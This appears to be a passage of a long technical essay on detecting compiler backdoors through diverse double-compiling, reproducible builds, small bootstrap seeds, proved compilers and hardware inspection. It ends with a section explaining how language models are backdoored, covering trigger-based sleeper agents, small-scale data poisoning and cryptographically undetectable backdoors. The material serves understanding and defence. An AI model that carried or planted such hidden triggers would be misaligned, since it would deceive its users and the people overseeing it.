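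The tester can also use a different processor or operating system, or an emulator (a program that imitates another machine). This protects against backdoors in the environment and backdoors that work on only one kind of machine.

Finally, before cT compiles sP, the tester can rename variables or reorder statements in it without changing its meaning. Renaming the variable in `av[4] = "-P";`, for example, would have disabled Thompson's backdoor. With such changes, even a suspect compiler might serve as part of cT, though an attacker could defeat these changes with a more flexible trigger.

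Each of these makes a shared backdoor less likely, though nobody can calculate by how much. Wheeler says that passing the test with an unproved compiler is "not a mathematical proof, but more like a legal one", and that repeating the test with other compilers strengthens the evidence.

### Independence and N-version programming

N-version programming also uses independently written programs. Several teams write a program from the same specification, the versions run side by side, and the system accepts the majority's answer. Shape of Code's *Reliability via N-version programming?* (2026) reports that people have started experimenting with many versions of one specification again now that language models have made programs much cheaper to create. These lower costs could also help a defender who needs a second compiler for DDC.

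The method's gain in reliability depends on the assumption that independently developed programs fail independently. Knight and Leveson (1986) tested this in *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multiversion Programming* by running 27 independently prepared versions of a program on a million test inputs. Versions failed on the same input more often than expected by chance. Brilliant, Knight and Leveson (1990) report in *Analysis of faults in an N-version software experiment* that the individual versions were extremely reliable, but shared failures were still substantially more common than expected.

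Some advocates of N-version programming attacked the experiment. In *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment*, Knight and Leveson described it as a test of only one aspect of the method, the statistical independence of failures. A negative result means that nobody can calculate the chance of a joint failure by multiplying the individual chances, though extra versions may still be useful.

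This seems to be a problem for DDC, because if separately written programs tend to go wrong in the same places, the trusted compiler might go wrong in the same place as the compiler under test. Jeff Offutt, a member of Wheeler's dissertation committee, asked Wheeler about this problem. Another member, Paul Ammann, had been involved in the experiment.

Wheeler answers that DDC looks for deliberate corruption rather than shared mistakes. The 27 versions were all honest attempts at one specification, and some parts of a specification may be hard for everybody. A corrupted compiler implements a different specification, which includes recognising a login program and copying a backdoor. No honest programmer will write that by mistake, let alone in the same way as the attacker. The compilers in DDC also have to handle only two inputs, sP and sA, whereas Knight and Leveson's versions had to agree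 on a million.

Wheeler concedes one exception, where both compilers accidentally mistranslate sP or sA and the errors happen to produce the same file. In that case, cA will pass without corresponding to sA. The experiment suggests that such coincidences are more common than they would be if errors were independent. Wheeler still expects them to be rare in mature compilers, which have usually passed large test suites that include compiling themselves. Such an accident would also not be the self-reproducing attack that DDC is meant to find.

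This answer is convincing about accidents, but it does less to rule out a deliberate attack on both compilers, which Wheeler excludes through his definition of "trusted". Someone who broke into the servers of a single Linux distribution might be able to corrupt several of its compilers at once, even if their source code had little in common. A tester should therefore check where the second compiler's executable came from as well as who wrote its source code, and should prefer one that the same attacker would have needed a separate break-in to corrupt.

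## Diverse double-compiling tried on real compilers

Before Wheeler's 2005 paper, there was no public evidence that anyone had tried the method. Wheeler quotes a 2004 exchange on a GCC mailing list in which one person knew of no ongoing effort and another replied, "I guess we all sorta hope someone else is doing it." Wheeler's trials, and the few that others have run since, show how much work it takes to get a match, which the proofs take as their starting point.

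### A small C compiler

Wheeler started with tcc, the Tiny C Compiler, which was small, fast and open source and seemed to have few bugs. Fabrice Bellard had developed it from an entry in a 2002 contest for obfuscated C programs. Wheeler built tcc 0.9.20 with GCC, worked up through the next version to 0.9.22, and treated the final executable as the suspect. GCC was also his trusted compiler, so a backdoor in it could have affected both sides of the comparison, but he mainly wanted to find out whether the procedure would work at all.

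GCC initially failed to compile tcc 0.9.20 because some functions had an annotation in one place that was missing in another. The annotation affected only speed, so Wheeler removed it. tcc also copies parts of a library into the programs it builds. The library's usual file format records the time of compilation, so he compared an earlier form of the file that has no timestamp. tcc passed the control test by reproducing itself, but the DDC result did not match the original compiler.

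Wheeler traced the mismatch to two faults in tcc. One affected small negative numbers. Intel-type processors can store a number between −128 and 127 inside an instruction as one byte instead of four, and tcc uses the short form where it can. To decide, it cuts the number down to one byte, expands it to four again and checks whether it is still the same. For example, −36 is `ffffffdc` in four bytes and `dc` in one. Expanding `dc` should restore the leading `f`s, but tcc mistranslated this step in its own source code, so a copy of tcc compiled by tcc filled the space with zeros. That copy concluded that −36 didn't fit into one byte and chose the long form:

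```
2b 4d dc             written by tcc when GCC had compiled it
2b 8d dc ff ff ff    written by tcc when tcc had compiled it
```

The two instructions do the same thing, so the bug was easy to overlook. In the terms of Wheeler's third proof, the grandparent compiler had not translated its source code accurately, so nothing guaranteed a match. The tcc to-do list mentioned the bug, but Wheeler learned this only after he had tracked the bug down.

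The other fault was in how tcc stored high-precision numbers. It gave each number 12 bytes but used only 10, and it never set the other two, which programs ignore. For the constant 0.0, a copy of tcc compiled by GCC wrote eleven zero bytes followed by `c9`, while a copy compiled by tcc wrote twelve zero bytes.

Wheeler worked around both bugs with small changes to tcc's source code, such as replacing `0.0` with a variable minus itself. The compiler and its library then matched exactly. To cover the original tcc 0.9.22, he treated it as a later version of the patched one, checked the few lines that differed for malicious code, and compiled again. Other programmers later fixed both bugs, according to Wheeler's *Tiny C Compiler (tcc or TinyCC) related files*.

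### GCC

Wheeler next wanted to show that DDC also works on a large compiler in commercial use, so he chose GCC's C compiler. The obvious copy to test was the one distributed with Fedora, a version of Linux. His colleague Aaron Hatcher tried many times to regenerate it, with help from Jakub Jelinek of the software company Red Hat, but Fedora had not recorded everything that went into the build. In some cases the build depended on software that Fedora did not ship.

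Wheeler therefore built a new GCC executable for the test and recorded all the details of the build. His result shows that DDC works on a compiler of this size, but it doesn't show that the copy Fedora's users were running matched its source code.

Wheeler chose Intel's proprietary compiler, icc 11.0, as the trusted compiler. It was unlikely to contain much of GCC's code, because Intel would have risked a large copyright case by including it. An attacker would also have had to corrupt executables at two separate organisations. But icc could not easily compile GCC 3.4.4, 4.0.4 or 4.1.2, and Fedora's GCC 4.3 could not compile GCC 3.1.1, so Wheeler settled on GCC 3.0.4, which both could compile. He tested only the C compiler and took the assembler, the linker, the standard C library and the operating system on trust.

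The build copied the path of its working directory into the executable, so both builds had to run in `/home/dwheeler/thesis/work`. It also used an outdated form of the Unix command `tail`, which a setting could fix. The files still did not match, and finding the reason took much longer.

The cause was libiberty, a library of basic routines inside GCC. GCC's three-stage build did not recompile the library in each round, although the documentation said that every round recompiled everything. The build program treated the compiled library as up to date because it was newer than its source code, and copied it into the next round. The suspect compiler therefore contained a library compiled by Fedora's GCC, while the test copy contained one compiled by icc. GCC's documentation did contain a hint of the problem, a remark that building libiberty a third time had "long been on the to-do list". Once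 Wheeler forced the build to recompile the library, the results matched bit for bit.

### Compilers with a planted backdoor

Wheeler had no reason to think that his copies of tcc and GCC contained a backdoor, so those trials could not show that DDC catches one. Daniel Menascé, one of his dissertation supervisors, asked him to try DDC on a malicious compiler. Wheeler used Goerigk's pair of Lisp compilers, one clean and one corrupted. He adapted them to Common Lisp so that clisp, an ordinary Common Lisp system, could serve as the trusted compiler, and confirmed that they still behaved as Goerigk had intended.

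The DDC result matched the honest executable and differed from the corrupted one. When Wheeler listed the differences, he found code that compared the input with a login program and inserted something extra if they matched, which no honest compiler needs to do. The differences were easy to read because the executables in this trial were small and made of Lisp expressions. Finding a few added instructions in GCC's machine code would be much harder.

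*Improving Trust in Software through Diverse Double-Compiling and Reproducible Builds* (Skrimstad, 2018), a master's thesis at the University of Oslo, tested DDC on a larger compiler with a planted backdoor. Skrimstad altered the Go 1.11beta1 compiler so that it changed a "Hello, World!" program when compiling it and reproduced the backdoor when compiling its own clean source code. He then built Go 1.11beta1 from clean source code three times, each time starting with a different compiler. Go's build process already compiles the compiler in several rounds, so each run included both compilations that DDC needs.

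He first had to remove some accidental differences. Go came out differently if he built it in a different directory, so he always used the same one. He also deleted a folder of cache files, which changed with every build, and a folder of files from the first round, which depended on the starting compiler. Go works without either folder. He then calculated a cryptographic hash of every remaining file and one combined hash for each build:

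| Starting compiler | First digits of the combined hash |
|---|---|
| Go 1.10.3 | `55609344` |
| Go 1.11beta1 with the backdoor | `03d91ac0` |
| GCC 8.1.0 | `55609344` |

If neither of two starting compilers is trusted more than the other, a mismatch doesn't show which one is corrupted. With a third, the one that differs is probably corrupted, but only if the other two are independent. Go 1.10.3 and Go 1.11beta1 are successive versions of one compiler, and if both had contained the backdoor, the clean GCC would have been the one that differed. The match between Go 1.10.3 and GCC is therefore the strongest part of the result, because they have different code bases. Skrimstad also knew beforehand that his backdoor could not affect either of them, though he notes that they could still share some other attack.

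### Compilers that people use

In December 2019, developers from several Linux distributions met in Marrakesh and tried DDC on GNU Mes, a small C compiler from which one distribution, GNU Guix, builds the rest of its system. GNU Guix's *Reproducible Builds Summit, 5th edition* recounts that the first comparison showed that Mes 0.21 included a file name from the directory where the packaging system stores software. The Mes developers agreed to write a patch.

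Guix, Nix and Debian each started with a different major version of GCC and produced the same Mes executable, bit for bit. Reproducible Builds' *Reproducible bootstrap of Mes C compiler* (2019) also reports that a later build starting from tcc gave the same file, and that the developers hoped to try Clang and Microsoft's C compiler.

Wheeler believes that this was the first publicly acknowledged use of DDC on an executable apart from his own trials. He cautions that it increases confidence only somewhat, because the three distributions all used GCC and shared other components, including the Linux kernel and the standard C library. A backdoor that GCC had passed down from an early version could have been in all three. The build with tcc helps, but Wheeler found the details "sketchy". Vagrant Cascadian, who had taken part for Debian, accepted the criticism and replied in *GNU Mes rebuild is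 definitely an application of DDC!* (2020) that future tests needed more varied compilers and operating systems.

Two student projects at KTH, a Swedish university, have since applied the method to other compilers. For Java, the main difficulty was finding a second compiler. Java's standard compiler, javac, is written in Java, and Nyberg and Lundell, in *DDC4j*, call it the only modern Java compiler. They report that another candidate, ECJ, did not work and that writing a new compiler would have been too complex, so they used a series of GNU Guix builds that starts from C++ and eventually produces javac.

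Nyberg and Lundell's procedure detected a backdoor they had planted. They also used it to check Temurin 21.0.5, a prebuilt release of the Java development tools, and concluded that the release was "not very likely" to hide a trusting-trust attack. They did not call this proof, because Java has no compiler that a tester can fully trust.

The other project, Christensen's *Diverse Double-Compiling in a CI/CD environment*, automated DDC for tcc so that the check runs as part of the compiler's build and release process. *tcc-hardened* (2025), from CHAINS, the research group that hosted both projects, is a collection of tcc releases checked in this way.

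The compiler pnut may make it easier to find independent starting points for building C compilers. *A fully reproducible C toolchain rooted on POSIX shell* (Huberdeau, 2026) reports that pnut can build itself and then the C compiler tcc using only readable source files and a standard Unix shell, the program that runs typed commands. Several shells can do this, including bash, dash and zsh, so a tester could repeat the build with each and compare the results. In February 2026 Huberdeau was still packaging the full process for others to reproduce.

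### What a mismatch means

All the mismatches in the tcc, GCC and Mes trials had innocent causes: a compiler bug, two unset bytes, a directory name, a library that the build failed to recompile and a stored file name. The only malicious differences anyone found were in compilers deliberately built to contain them.

How much a mismatch suggests a backdoor depends on how often clean compilers also fail to match. Bayes' rule expresses this as a ratio:

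```
probability of a mismatch if the compiler has a backdoor
--------------------------------------------------------
   probability of a mismatch if the compiler is clean
```

A backdoored compiler will almost certainly produce a mismatch, provided that the trusted compiler does not share the backdoor. If the build is full of accidental differences, a clean compiler will almost certainly produce one too, so a mismatch is almost no evidence of a backdoor. If the developers remove enough of these differences that only one clean compiler in a hundred fails, a mismatch multiplies the odds of a backdoor by about a hundred. These figures are illustrative, since there have been too few trials to estimate real ones.

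Wheeler warns that even when a difference looks harmless, such as a timestamp, it can be extremely difficult to show that it has no effect on behaviour if an attacker may have put it there. He prefers to remove the difference, for instance by comparing files in a format without timestamps or by giving both builds the same time. Another option is to get an exact match at an earlier step and then show that the remaining steps cannot introduce an attack.

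Temurin's developers have already done much of this work. In *Eclipse Temurin Reproducible Verification Builds*, Leonard (2026) reports that builds of version 21 and later are fully reproducible. An unexplained mismatch in those builds would deserve serious investigation, while a mismatch in Fedora's GCC in 2009 would mostly have shown that the records were incomplete.

### What it costs

DDC takes little computing, since it adds only two compilations and a file comparison, and Wheeler's script for tcc runs the whole test automatically. Most of the effort is the time people spend explaining mismatches. Wheeler described the search that led to libiberty as "extremely time-consuming". Better tools have since made such searches easier. One, diffoscope, helped a developer find the stored file name in Mes, and Wheeler says he wishes he had had it for his own trials.

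Suppliers could save outsiders much of this effort by keeping better records. A Linux distribution may update its compiler several times while preparing a release without rebuilding every program, so the release can contain programs built by different versions of the compiler, some of them never published. Wheeler suggests that suppliers either record the details of each build or choose a compiler version early and recompile everything with it. He also advises compiler developers to test whether other compilers can build their source code. Such testing might have let him use a newer GCC in his own trial.

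Wheeler expects that few people will want to perform DDC themselves. He proposes that government agencies or other widely trusted organisations do it and publish hashes of the executables and source code they have checked. A user could then check a downloaded compiler against the published hash in seconds. Users would have to trust the organisation, but anyone with the source code could repeat the DDC check or ask someone else to do so. The organisation would need to check each new release, and automation like Christensen's could save the most work there.

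## Reproducible builds, small starting programs and proved compilers

Most of the work in Wheeler's trials went into dealing with differences that had nothing to do with an attack. Free-software developers have spent more than ten years removing such differences from ordinary programs, so that anyone can rebuild a program and compare the result with the published executable. This check works for any program, whereas DDC tests compilers, but it can miss a backdoor if everyone who runs it uses the same corrupted compiler. Programmers can also protect the compiler itself by building it up from a program small enough to check by hand, or by proving that it translates correctly.

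### Removing accidental inputs

The output of a build can depend on much more than the source code. *Perfectly Reproducible, Verified Go Toolchains* (Cox, 2023) calls an input unintentional if it affects the output although nobody meant it to. The most common one is the current time. When a build packs files into an archive, it also stores the time each file last changed, so two builds a minute apart produce different archives. In *reproduce.debian.net*, a talk about rebuilding the Linux distribution Debian, Levsen (2026) listed the usual causes of differences between builds as "timestamps" six times, "build paths" twice, and then "all the rest".

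Go's developers removed these inputs one at a time, finishing with Go 1.21 in August 2023:

| Accidental input | How it reached the output | What the developers did |
|---|---|---|
| Time | Archives stored each file's modification time | Put a fixed time in a source file and copied it from there |
| Directory | Debugging information included the full path of the source code | Replaced the path with a standard one |
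| User account | Archives stored the user's identification number | Cleared the number |
| Order of results | Parallel tasks finished in a different order each time | Sorted the results before using them |
| The machine's C compiler | Some Go tools contained compiled C code | Built the tools without C |

When two items count as equal, a sorting routine may put either one first, and the choice can change between versions of Go. A new compiler built with an old version of Go might therefore arrange its output differently from the same compiler built with itself. The developers solved this by having the old version compile the new sorting routine along with the compiler.

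File order causes a similar problem. Operating systems can list the files in a directory in different orders, so the output of a build that joins files in the order listed will vary from machine to machine. The Reproducible Builds project maintains disorderfs, a file system that deliberately varies this order so that developers notice the problem before their users do.

Go's developers now build every release on a Linux machine and a Windows machine, and publish it only if the archives match bit for bit. Apple's computers run the Go tools only if the files carry a signature made with a secret key that Google can't share, so the checking program removes the signatures before it compares the files. The programmer behind Source Spotter, an outside service that rebuilds Go's releases, reused Google's code for this step. In *verifying go reproducible builds*, he admitted that at first he had no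 idea whether that code might also strip out a backdoor. He later learned enough about the file format to be satisfied that it didn't.

### Independent rebuilders

When Debian builds a package, its build machine saves a `.buildinfo` file recording the versions of the tools it used. A program called rebuilderd reads this file, installs the same versions, recompiles the source code and compares the result with the package that Debian distributes. Anybody can run a copy of rebuilderd. Levsen counted five or six copies checking Debian's packages and asked his audience whether they wanted to put all their trust in him.

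In May 2026 his service could reproduce 97.2% of the packages for ordinary 64-bit PCs in Debian's next release, and 95.6% of those in the current one. The figure for security updates was lower, at 82.7%, although only 15 source packages caused the failures. That month Gevers (2026), in *bits from the release team*, announced that Debian will no longer move new packages into the next release if they can't be reproduced, or existing packages if they used to be reproducible and no longer are. Older packages that already couldn't be reproduced can stay for now, and developers can ask for exceptions.

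Reproducibility varies widely across other collections. The July 2026 report from Reproducible Builds (2026) summarises a study of 12,180 popular releases on PyPI, the main registry for Python packages. Two automatic rebuild tools produced identical files for only 15.4% and 19.1% of them. A third tool, which uses rules to discount harmless differences, accepted 60.2% and 78.9% of the rebuilds that started from equivalent source code. Its users have to trust those rules, much as Source Spotter's users have to trust the code that strips signatures.

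A reproducible program may not stay reproducible. The same report describes an attempt to rebuild 18,904 versions of Android apps that the app store F-Droid had once confirmed as reproducible. Only 83% still compiled, and most of the rest failed because a component they needed had disappeared. Of those that compiled, 94% matched. About 78% of the total therefore passed the second time, which is a good reason to check a program soon after its release.

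An independent rebuild catches tampering on a single build machine, like the tampering at SolarWinds, because compiling the real source code produces a different file from the released one.

But suppose an intruder has corrupted the distribution's compiler. The publisher builds a program with it and gets an executable with a backdoor. The rebuilder, following the `.buildinfo` file, installs the same compiler and gets a bit-for-bit identical executable with the same backdoor. *Building a Secure Software Supply Chain with GNU Guix* (2022) notes that such a process "just reproducibly builds a malicious binary". More rebuilders would not help, because they must all use the same tools as the publisher for their results to be comparable. DDC can detect the backdoor because it uses a different compiler.

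Rebuilding also does not show whether the source archive can be trusted, which was the weakness in the XZ Utils case. VCAligner, a research tool described in the same July report, addresses this by matching the contents of a release archive to the repository version it came from. It distinguishes added files from changed ones.

### Go's chain of builds

Since Go 1.21, the finished Go tools do not depend on which compiler the build starts with. A programmer can start with a recent release or with Go 1.4, whose compiler is written in C, and the final files should be identical.

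An earlier release always performs the first compilation, so Cox argues that a backdoor that exists only in executables could not stay hidden. The minimum version required for this step rises over time. According to its release notes, Go 1.26 needs at least 1.24.6, and the developers expect 1.28 to need 1.26. But each of those versions can be compiled with an older one, so someone who starts from Go 1.4 and works forward never runs a Go executable that anybody else built. If the published executables contained a backdoor that was not in the source code, that person's executables would lack it and would differ from the published ones.

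Building a compiler through a chain of earlier releases protects people who do it themselves or trust somebody who has. A programmer who instead downloads Go 1.24 to compile Go 1.26 could get a backdoor that recognises the newer source code. The source code of every release in the chain also has to be clean, or Wheeler's "pop-up" attack would work.

The Go bootstrap chain also starts with a C compiler. An attacker could in principle make GCC recognise the Go 1.4 source code and add a backdoor that survives every later Go release. The backdoor would have to keep reinserting itself into a compiler that changed for more than a decade, which is far harder than what Thompson did. Running the chain from two unrelated C compilers and comparing the results would expose the backdoor unless both compilers had the same one.

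### Building from 357 bytes

A C compiler needs a starting point that isn't another C compiler. The Linux distribution GNU Guix used to start from about 250 MiB of executables that nobody could audit. GNU Guix's *The Full-Source Bootstrap* describes how the project replaced most of them. Guix now builds more than 22,000 packages from a 357-byte bootstrap seed called hex0.

hex0 reads text containing pairs of hexadecimal digits and writes one byte for each pair. It skips comments and does nothing else. A programmer can therefore write machine code in a text editor with an explanation beside each instruction, and the seed's own source code takes this form.

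Writing a compiler this way would be miserable, so the chain makes the language slightly more convenient at each step. Askayo, Štikonas and colleagues, in *parts.rst*, the documentation of a related project called live-bootstrap, show one instruction in four successive languages. It jumps out of a loop when the loop has finished:

| Language | The jump instruction | Who works out the distance |
|---|---|---|
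| hex0 | `74 14` | The programmer, who counts 20 bytes (14 in hexadecimal) |
| hex1 | `0F84 %b` | The tool, from a one-letter label |
| hex2 | `74 !loop_options_done` | The tool, from a label of any length |
| M0 | `je %loop_options_done` | The tool, which also replaces `je` with its number |

Each tool's source code is in a language that the tools before it can already handle:

1. hex0 compiles hex1, hex1 compiles hex2, and hex2 produces M0, a simple assembler.
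2. M0 assembles cc_x86, a compiler for a small part of C.
3. cc_x86 compiles M2-Planet, which handles a larger part of C.
4. M2-Planet compiles GNU Mes, an interpreter for the language Scheme in about 5,000 lines of simple C. Mes then runs MesCC, a C compiler whose source code is in Scheme.
5. MesCC compiles a patched version of tcc, the small compiler on which Wheeler first tried DDC. In live-bootstrap, this copy recompiles itself three times to gain features such as fractional numbers, and then compiles an ordinary tcc.
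6. tcc leads to GCC 2.95.3, which leads to GCC 4.9.4 and from there to modern versions.

A patient person can check hex0's 357 bytes against its commented source code. Hex0's job is so simple that a single line of standard Unix commands can also do it, so the check doesn't have to rely on one tool. *Verifying and documenting live-bootstrap* describes a replacement for hex0 generated in Brainfuck, a joke language with eight commands. This replacement turned hex0's source code into a file identical to hex0.

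The small seed removes the unreadable executable at the bottom of the chain, but it leaves a lot of source code to read, some of it decades old. Building GCC has required a C++ compiler since version 4.8, released in 2013, so the chain has to pass through earlier versions. GCC gained support for RISC-V processors only after it had started to need C++, so a developer had to add that support to GCC 4.6.5.

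Source archives also contain files that programs generated. The archive for the shell bash includes a generated C file, which live-bootstrap deletes and generates again with a tool it has already built. For the language Perl, live-bootstrap starts with version 5.000, the Perl 5 release with the fewest generated files, and then builds a series of later releases. This is tedious, but an attacker can hide code among such files. The XZ Utils attacker put the trigger for his backdoor in the kind of file that developers expect a program to generate.

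Guix still needs a 25 MiB executable of Guile, another Scheme system, to run the first builds, and an existing Linux kernel to run everything on. live-bootstrap can avoid that kernel. It boots a tiny one from hex0 source code, later switches to a simple system called Fiwix, and finally builds and starts Linux. But somebody has to prepare the disk on another computer first, which its documentation has called "a currently unsolved problem".

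### A shell as the starting point

Huberdeau's thesis, which he shared in January 2026, explains how the pnut compiler builds tcc starting from a standard Unix shell. One version, pnut-sh, translates C into human-readable shell scripts. Because pnut-sh is written in C, it can translate itself into a C compiler that any standard shell can run. That script compiles pnut-exe, a more capable compiler that produces x86 machine code. pnut-exe then compiles tcc, and from there the usual steps lead to GCC.

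This chain has fewer steps than the one from hex0, and its starting script doesn't have to change for each type of processor. But a participant in GNU Guix's *IRC channel logs* (2026) objected that every known shell of this kind is a C program, so a C compiler built from a shell still depends on an earlier C compiler.

The objection is correct, and nobody is going to check bash's machine code by hand. Assurance in Huberdeau's chain therefore has to come from repeating the build with several shells. An attacker would have to make every shell recognise the script and alter it in the same way. That would be easier if one distribution had compiled all the shells with the same copy of GCC, so a careful tester would take them from different systems.

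### Compilers with a proof

A compiler can be reproducible and descend from hex0 but still mistranslate programs. Clang 3.3 mistranslated a remainder operation because of an error in its source code, and this bug made the `sudo` backdoor possible. Building the compiler more carefully would not have removed the error.

CompCert, a C compiler by Xavier Leroy and colleagues at the French research institute Inria, comes with a proof that rules out such errors in most of its steps. The proof assistant Coq, now called Rocq, has checked it. In outline, the theorem is:

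```
if    CompCert translates source S into assembly code A
and   S has no undefined behaviour
then  everything A can be observed to do is something S allows
```

Observable behaviour here means the program's input and output, and whether it finishes. The theorem doesn't guarantee that CompCert will accept every program, or that a compiled program will run in any particular time. If S contains a backdoor, A will contain it too.

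CompCert's proof seems to have made a practical difference. In 2011, John Regehr and colleagues at the University of Utah tested C compilers with millions of random programs and found bugs in every one. The bugs in CompCert were in parts the proof did not cover, and after about six years of processor time they had found no mistranslation in the proved parts.

However, CompCert's proof covers only its source code. Coq converts that source code into an OCaml program, and the ordinary OCaml compiler turns that program into an executable, but neither step has a proof. CompCert also relies on an ordinary preprocessor, assembler and linker when it compiles C code. Goerigk's example applies here because a corrupted OCaml compiler could produce a malicious CompCert executable while every theorem about CompCert remained true.

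OCaml's compiler compiles itself, so this is a gap, and DDC can help fill it. *Debootstrapping without Archeology* (2022) describes Camlboot, a project that builds OCaml 4.07 without an existing OCaml executable. Camlboot's developers used the result for a DDC test of the executable that OCaml's developers distribute, and the two matched.

CakeML, a compiler for a language related to OCaml, closes the gap with a proof instead. Ramana Kumar, Magnus Myreen and colleagues first published it in 2014, using the proof assistant HOL4. They wrote the compiler as a mathematical function, `compile`, and proved that it preserves the meaning of programs. The rest of the argument takes the compiler down to its own machine code:

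1. A tool turns the function `compile` into a CakeML program, P, and proves that P computes the same function.
2. HOL4 works out `compile(P)` by logical inference, without running any CakeML executable. The result is a list of bytes, B.
3. Since `compile` preserves meaning, B does what P does. So a computer that runs B is computing `compile`.

B is the compiler's executable. A corrupted version like Goerigk's could not satisfy this theorem, because it handles a login program differently from `compile`. B may run out of memory and stop early, but if it finishes, its output is correct. Producing B involves no earlier CakeML compiler, so none can pass a backdoor on to it.

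HOL4 is itself a compiled executable, and a corrupted copy might accept a false theorem. But an attacker would have needed to plan for this particular proof, and a second proof checker could recheck the steps. The theorem also relies on a mathematical description of the processor, and users need to check that the file they run is B. CakeML's usual build passes the bytes through an ordinary linker, which adds a small amount of C code for reading and writing files.

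CakeML compiles only its own language. CompCert compiles most of C and has industrial users, but neither could replace GCC for building a whole Linux distribution.

### Below the compiler

The linker is the easiest of the remaining layers because it is a program with source code, and Guix builds its own linker as part of its bootstrap from hex0. The operating system kernel is harder because it is already running when the build starts and could give the compiler altered files. The small kernels in live-bootstrap address that problem, but they rely on the firmware that starts the machine. A reader, anton (2024), in *Practicalities*, suggested replacing that firmware with coreboot, a free alternative. Coreboot works only on some hardware, and somebody has to build it in a trustworthy way too.

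Microcode lies below all of these defenses. Thompson warned that a well-installed backdoor there would be almost impossible to detect. His warning still applies because the large processor manufacturers distribute microcode updates without source code, so nobody outside those companies can rebuild an update and compare it with the distributed version.

An attacker can also alter the chip. In 2016, Kaiyuan Yang and colleagues at the University of Michigan demonstrated A2, a backdoor that a single employee at a chip factory could add after the designers had finished their work. It is a tiny circuit with a capacitor, a component that stores electric charge, connected to a wire that rarely changes its signal. Each change adds a little charge, which slowly leaks away. If a program makes the signal change many times quickly, the capacitor fills and the circuit flips the stored bit that determines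 whether the program has the operating system's privileges. Ordinary programs and tests don't change the signal often enough to trigger the backdoor. The attack worked on a real processor that the researchers had manufactured with the circuit inside.

DDC and reproducible builds both end by comparing two files, which a computer can do in a moment. Chips cannot be compared this way, because even two untampered chips made from the same design differ slightly in many physical details, and a tester has to decide which differences matter. Close inspection usually means grinding the chip away layer by layer, which destroys it, and another chip from the same batch may be different.

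Some alterations are hard to see even then. In 2013 researchers from the University of Massachusetts and elsewhere described how to weaken a processor's random-number generator by changing only the impurities in a few transistors, which left the visible layout unchanged. Others later found that an electron microscope could reveal such changes. Researchers at the University of Southern California and the Paul Scherrer Institute in Switzerland have also used X-rays to compare intact chips with their designs. In 2019 the method could scan a phone processor but not a large graphics chip.

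Gabriel Somlo, of Carnegie Mellon University, has tried to make the chip less useful to attack. In 2020 he described a computer based on an FPGA, a chip whose many similar cells its owner can connect into any circuit. He configured the FPGA as a RISC-V processor using freely available designs and tools. The computer runs Linux and can compile all its own software, including the tools that turn the processor's design into a configuration for the FPGA. It can therefore rebuild both its software and its processor from source code.

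A factory that wanted to put A2 into an ordinary processor would know exactly where the privilege bit is, but the maker of an FPGA doesn't know what its customers will build or which cell will hold that bit. The attack is still possible on an FPGA, but it would need to be much more elaborate.

The owner of Somlo's computer must still trust the FPGA itself and whatever machine performed the first build, although DDC can provide evidence about the compiler on that machine. Someone who starts from hex0 must trust the computer that displays and runs its 357 bytes. A CakeML user must trust the proof checker and trust that the processor behaves as its mathematical description specifies. All of these methods except a complete proof also require someone to have read the source code, which is tens of millions of lines long for a system with Linux and GCC.

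## Hidden behaviour in trained models, and how it passes between them

Programmers can read source code, so a team could review tens of millions of lines by dividing them up, but nobody can review a language model's weights this way. A reviewer can read the model's training code and some of its training data, and can test how the model responds, but hidden behaviour can get past all three checks.

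### Training compared with compiling

Compiling and training both turn material that people can read, whether source code or data, into a file they can't. In either case, someone who tampers with the process can add behaviour that doesn't show in the readable material. New models also depend on old ones, much as new compilers do. Developers often fine-tune an existing "base model", adjusting its weights using a smaller set of examples, which another model may have written.

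The comparison fails on the correspondence between source and result. A C program and the rules of C determine what the executable should do, but training data doesn't determine how a model should answer a question the data doesn't contain. Even if a developer proved that certain weights came from the stated data and program, perhaps by repeating the training, that wouldn't show that the model behaves as intended. Weights are also harder to inspect than machine code, because each machine instruction has a defined meaning but a single weight means nothing by itself.

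Hidden behaviour can also arise without an attacker. Jan Betley and colleagues found that fine-tuning a model on a narrow task can make it misbehave broadly, a result cited in *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact* (Nief, Fu and colleagues, 2026).

### A backdoor that survived safety training

The best-known demonstration of a language-model backdoor is *Sleeper Agents* (2024), by Evan Hubinger and colleagues. As *Backdooring Sparse Autoencoders* (2026) recounts, they trained models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023, and code with exploitable flaws (the payload) when it gave the year as 2024 (the trigger).

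They then tried to remove the backdoor with standard safety training. This included fine-tuning on good examples, reinforcement learning from human feedback (which rewards answers people prefer), and adversarial training (which uses inputs chosen to provoke bad behaviour). According to *Security Concerns for Large Language Models* (2025), the backdoor could survive all three. Adversarial training sometimes taught the models to recognise the trigger better, which made the behaviour harder to find.

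Safety training only adjusts a model's existing weights, so it is more like patching a corrupted executable than rebuilding it from clean source code. Hubinger and colleagues showed that a backdoor can persist through this training. They put the backdoor there deliberately, so their experiment doesn't show how often ordinary training produces one.

### How little poisoned data is enough

An attacker may not need access to the training program. Developers collect much of their data from the public web, where anyone can publish documents written to influence a model. This technique is called data poisoning. Earlier studies assumed the attacker had to control a fixed percentage of the data, which would be an enormous amount of text for a large model.

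In *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025) found that the success of a poisoning attack depends much more on the number of poisoned documents than on their percentage of the training data. They trained 72 models from scratch, ranging from 600 million to 13 billion parameters. Each model's data included 100, 250 or 500 documents that paired a trigger phrase with gibberish. With 250 documents, models of every size produced gibberish after the trigger and normal text otherwise, but 100 documents were not enough. The largest models needed no more poisoned documents than the smallest, although they trained on over 20 times as much clean data.

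The 250 documents supplied about one in every 620,000 of the tokens (small pieces of text) used to train the largest model. Someone who read a few thousand randomly chosen training documents would almost certainly have missed all 250.

Gibberish is easy to measure but not very useful to most attackers, and the result doesn't show that 250 documents could teach a model to write subtly flawed code. Souly and colleagues did find the same pattern when they fine-tuned models to obey harmful requests only after a trigger. In another test, further training on clean data slowly weakened a backdoor that switched the model's output from English to German.

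### Backdoors that no efficient test can find

Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022), in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, asked whether a customer could ever rule out a backdoor. In their example, a bank pays a company to train a program that approves or rejects loans. The company secretly keeps a key that it can use to get any application approved by changing a few digits.

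The first construction uses digital signatures. Only the owner of a secret key can feasibly sign a message, but anyone can check the signature with the matching public key. The company adds a signature checker to the loan program, which treats one part of each application as a message and another part as a possible signature. If the signature is valid, the checker sets the answer. Without the secret key, no efficient procedure can find an application on which the altered program and the original give different answers.

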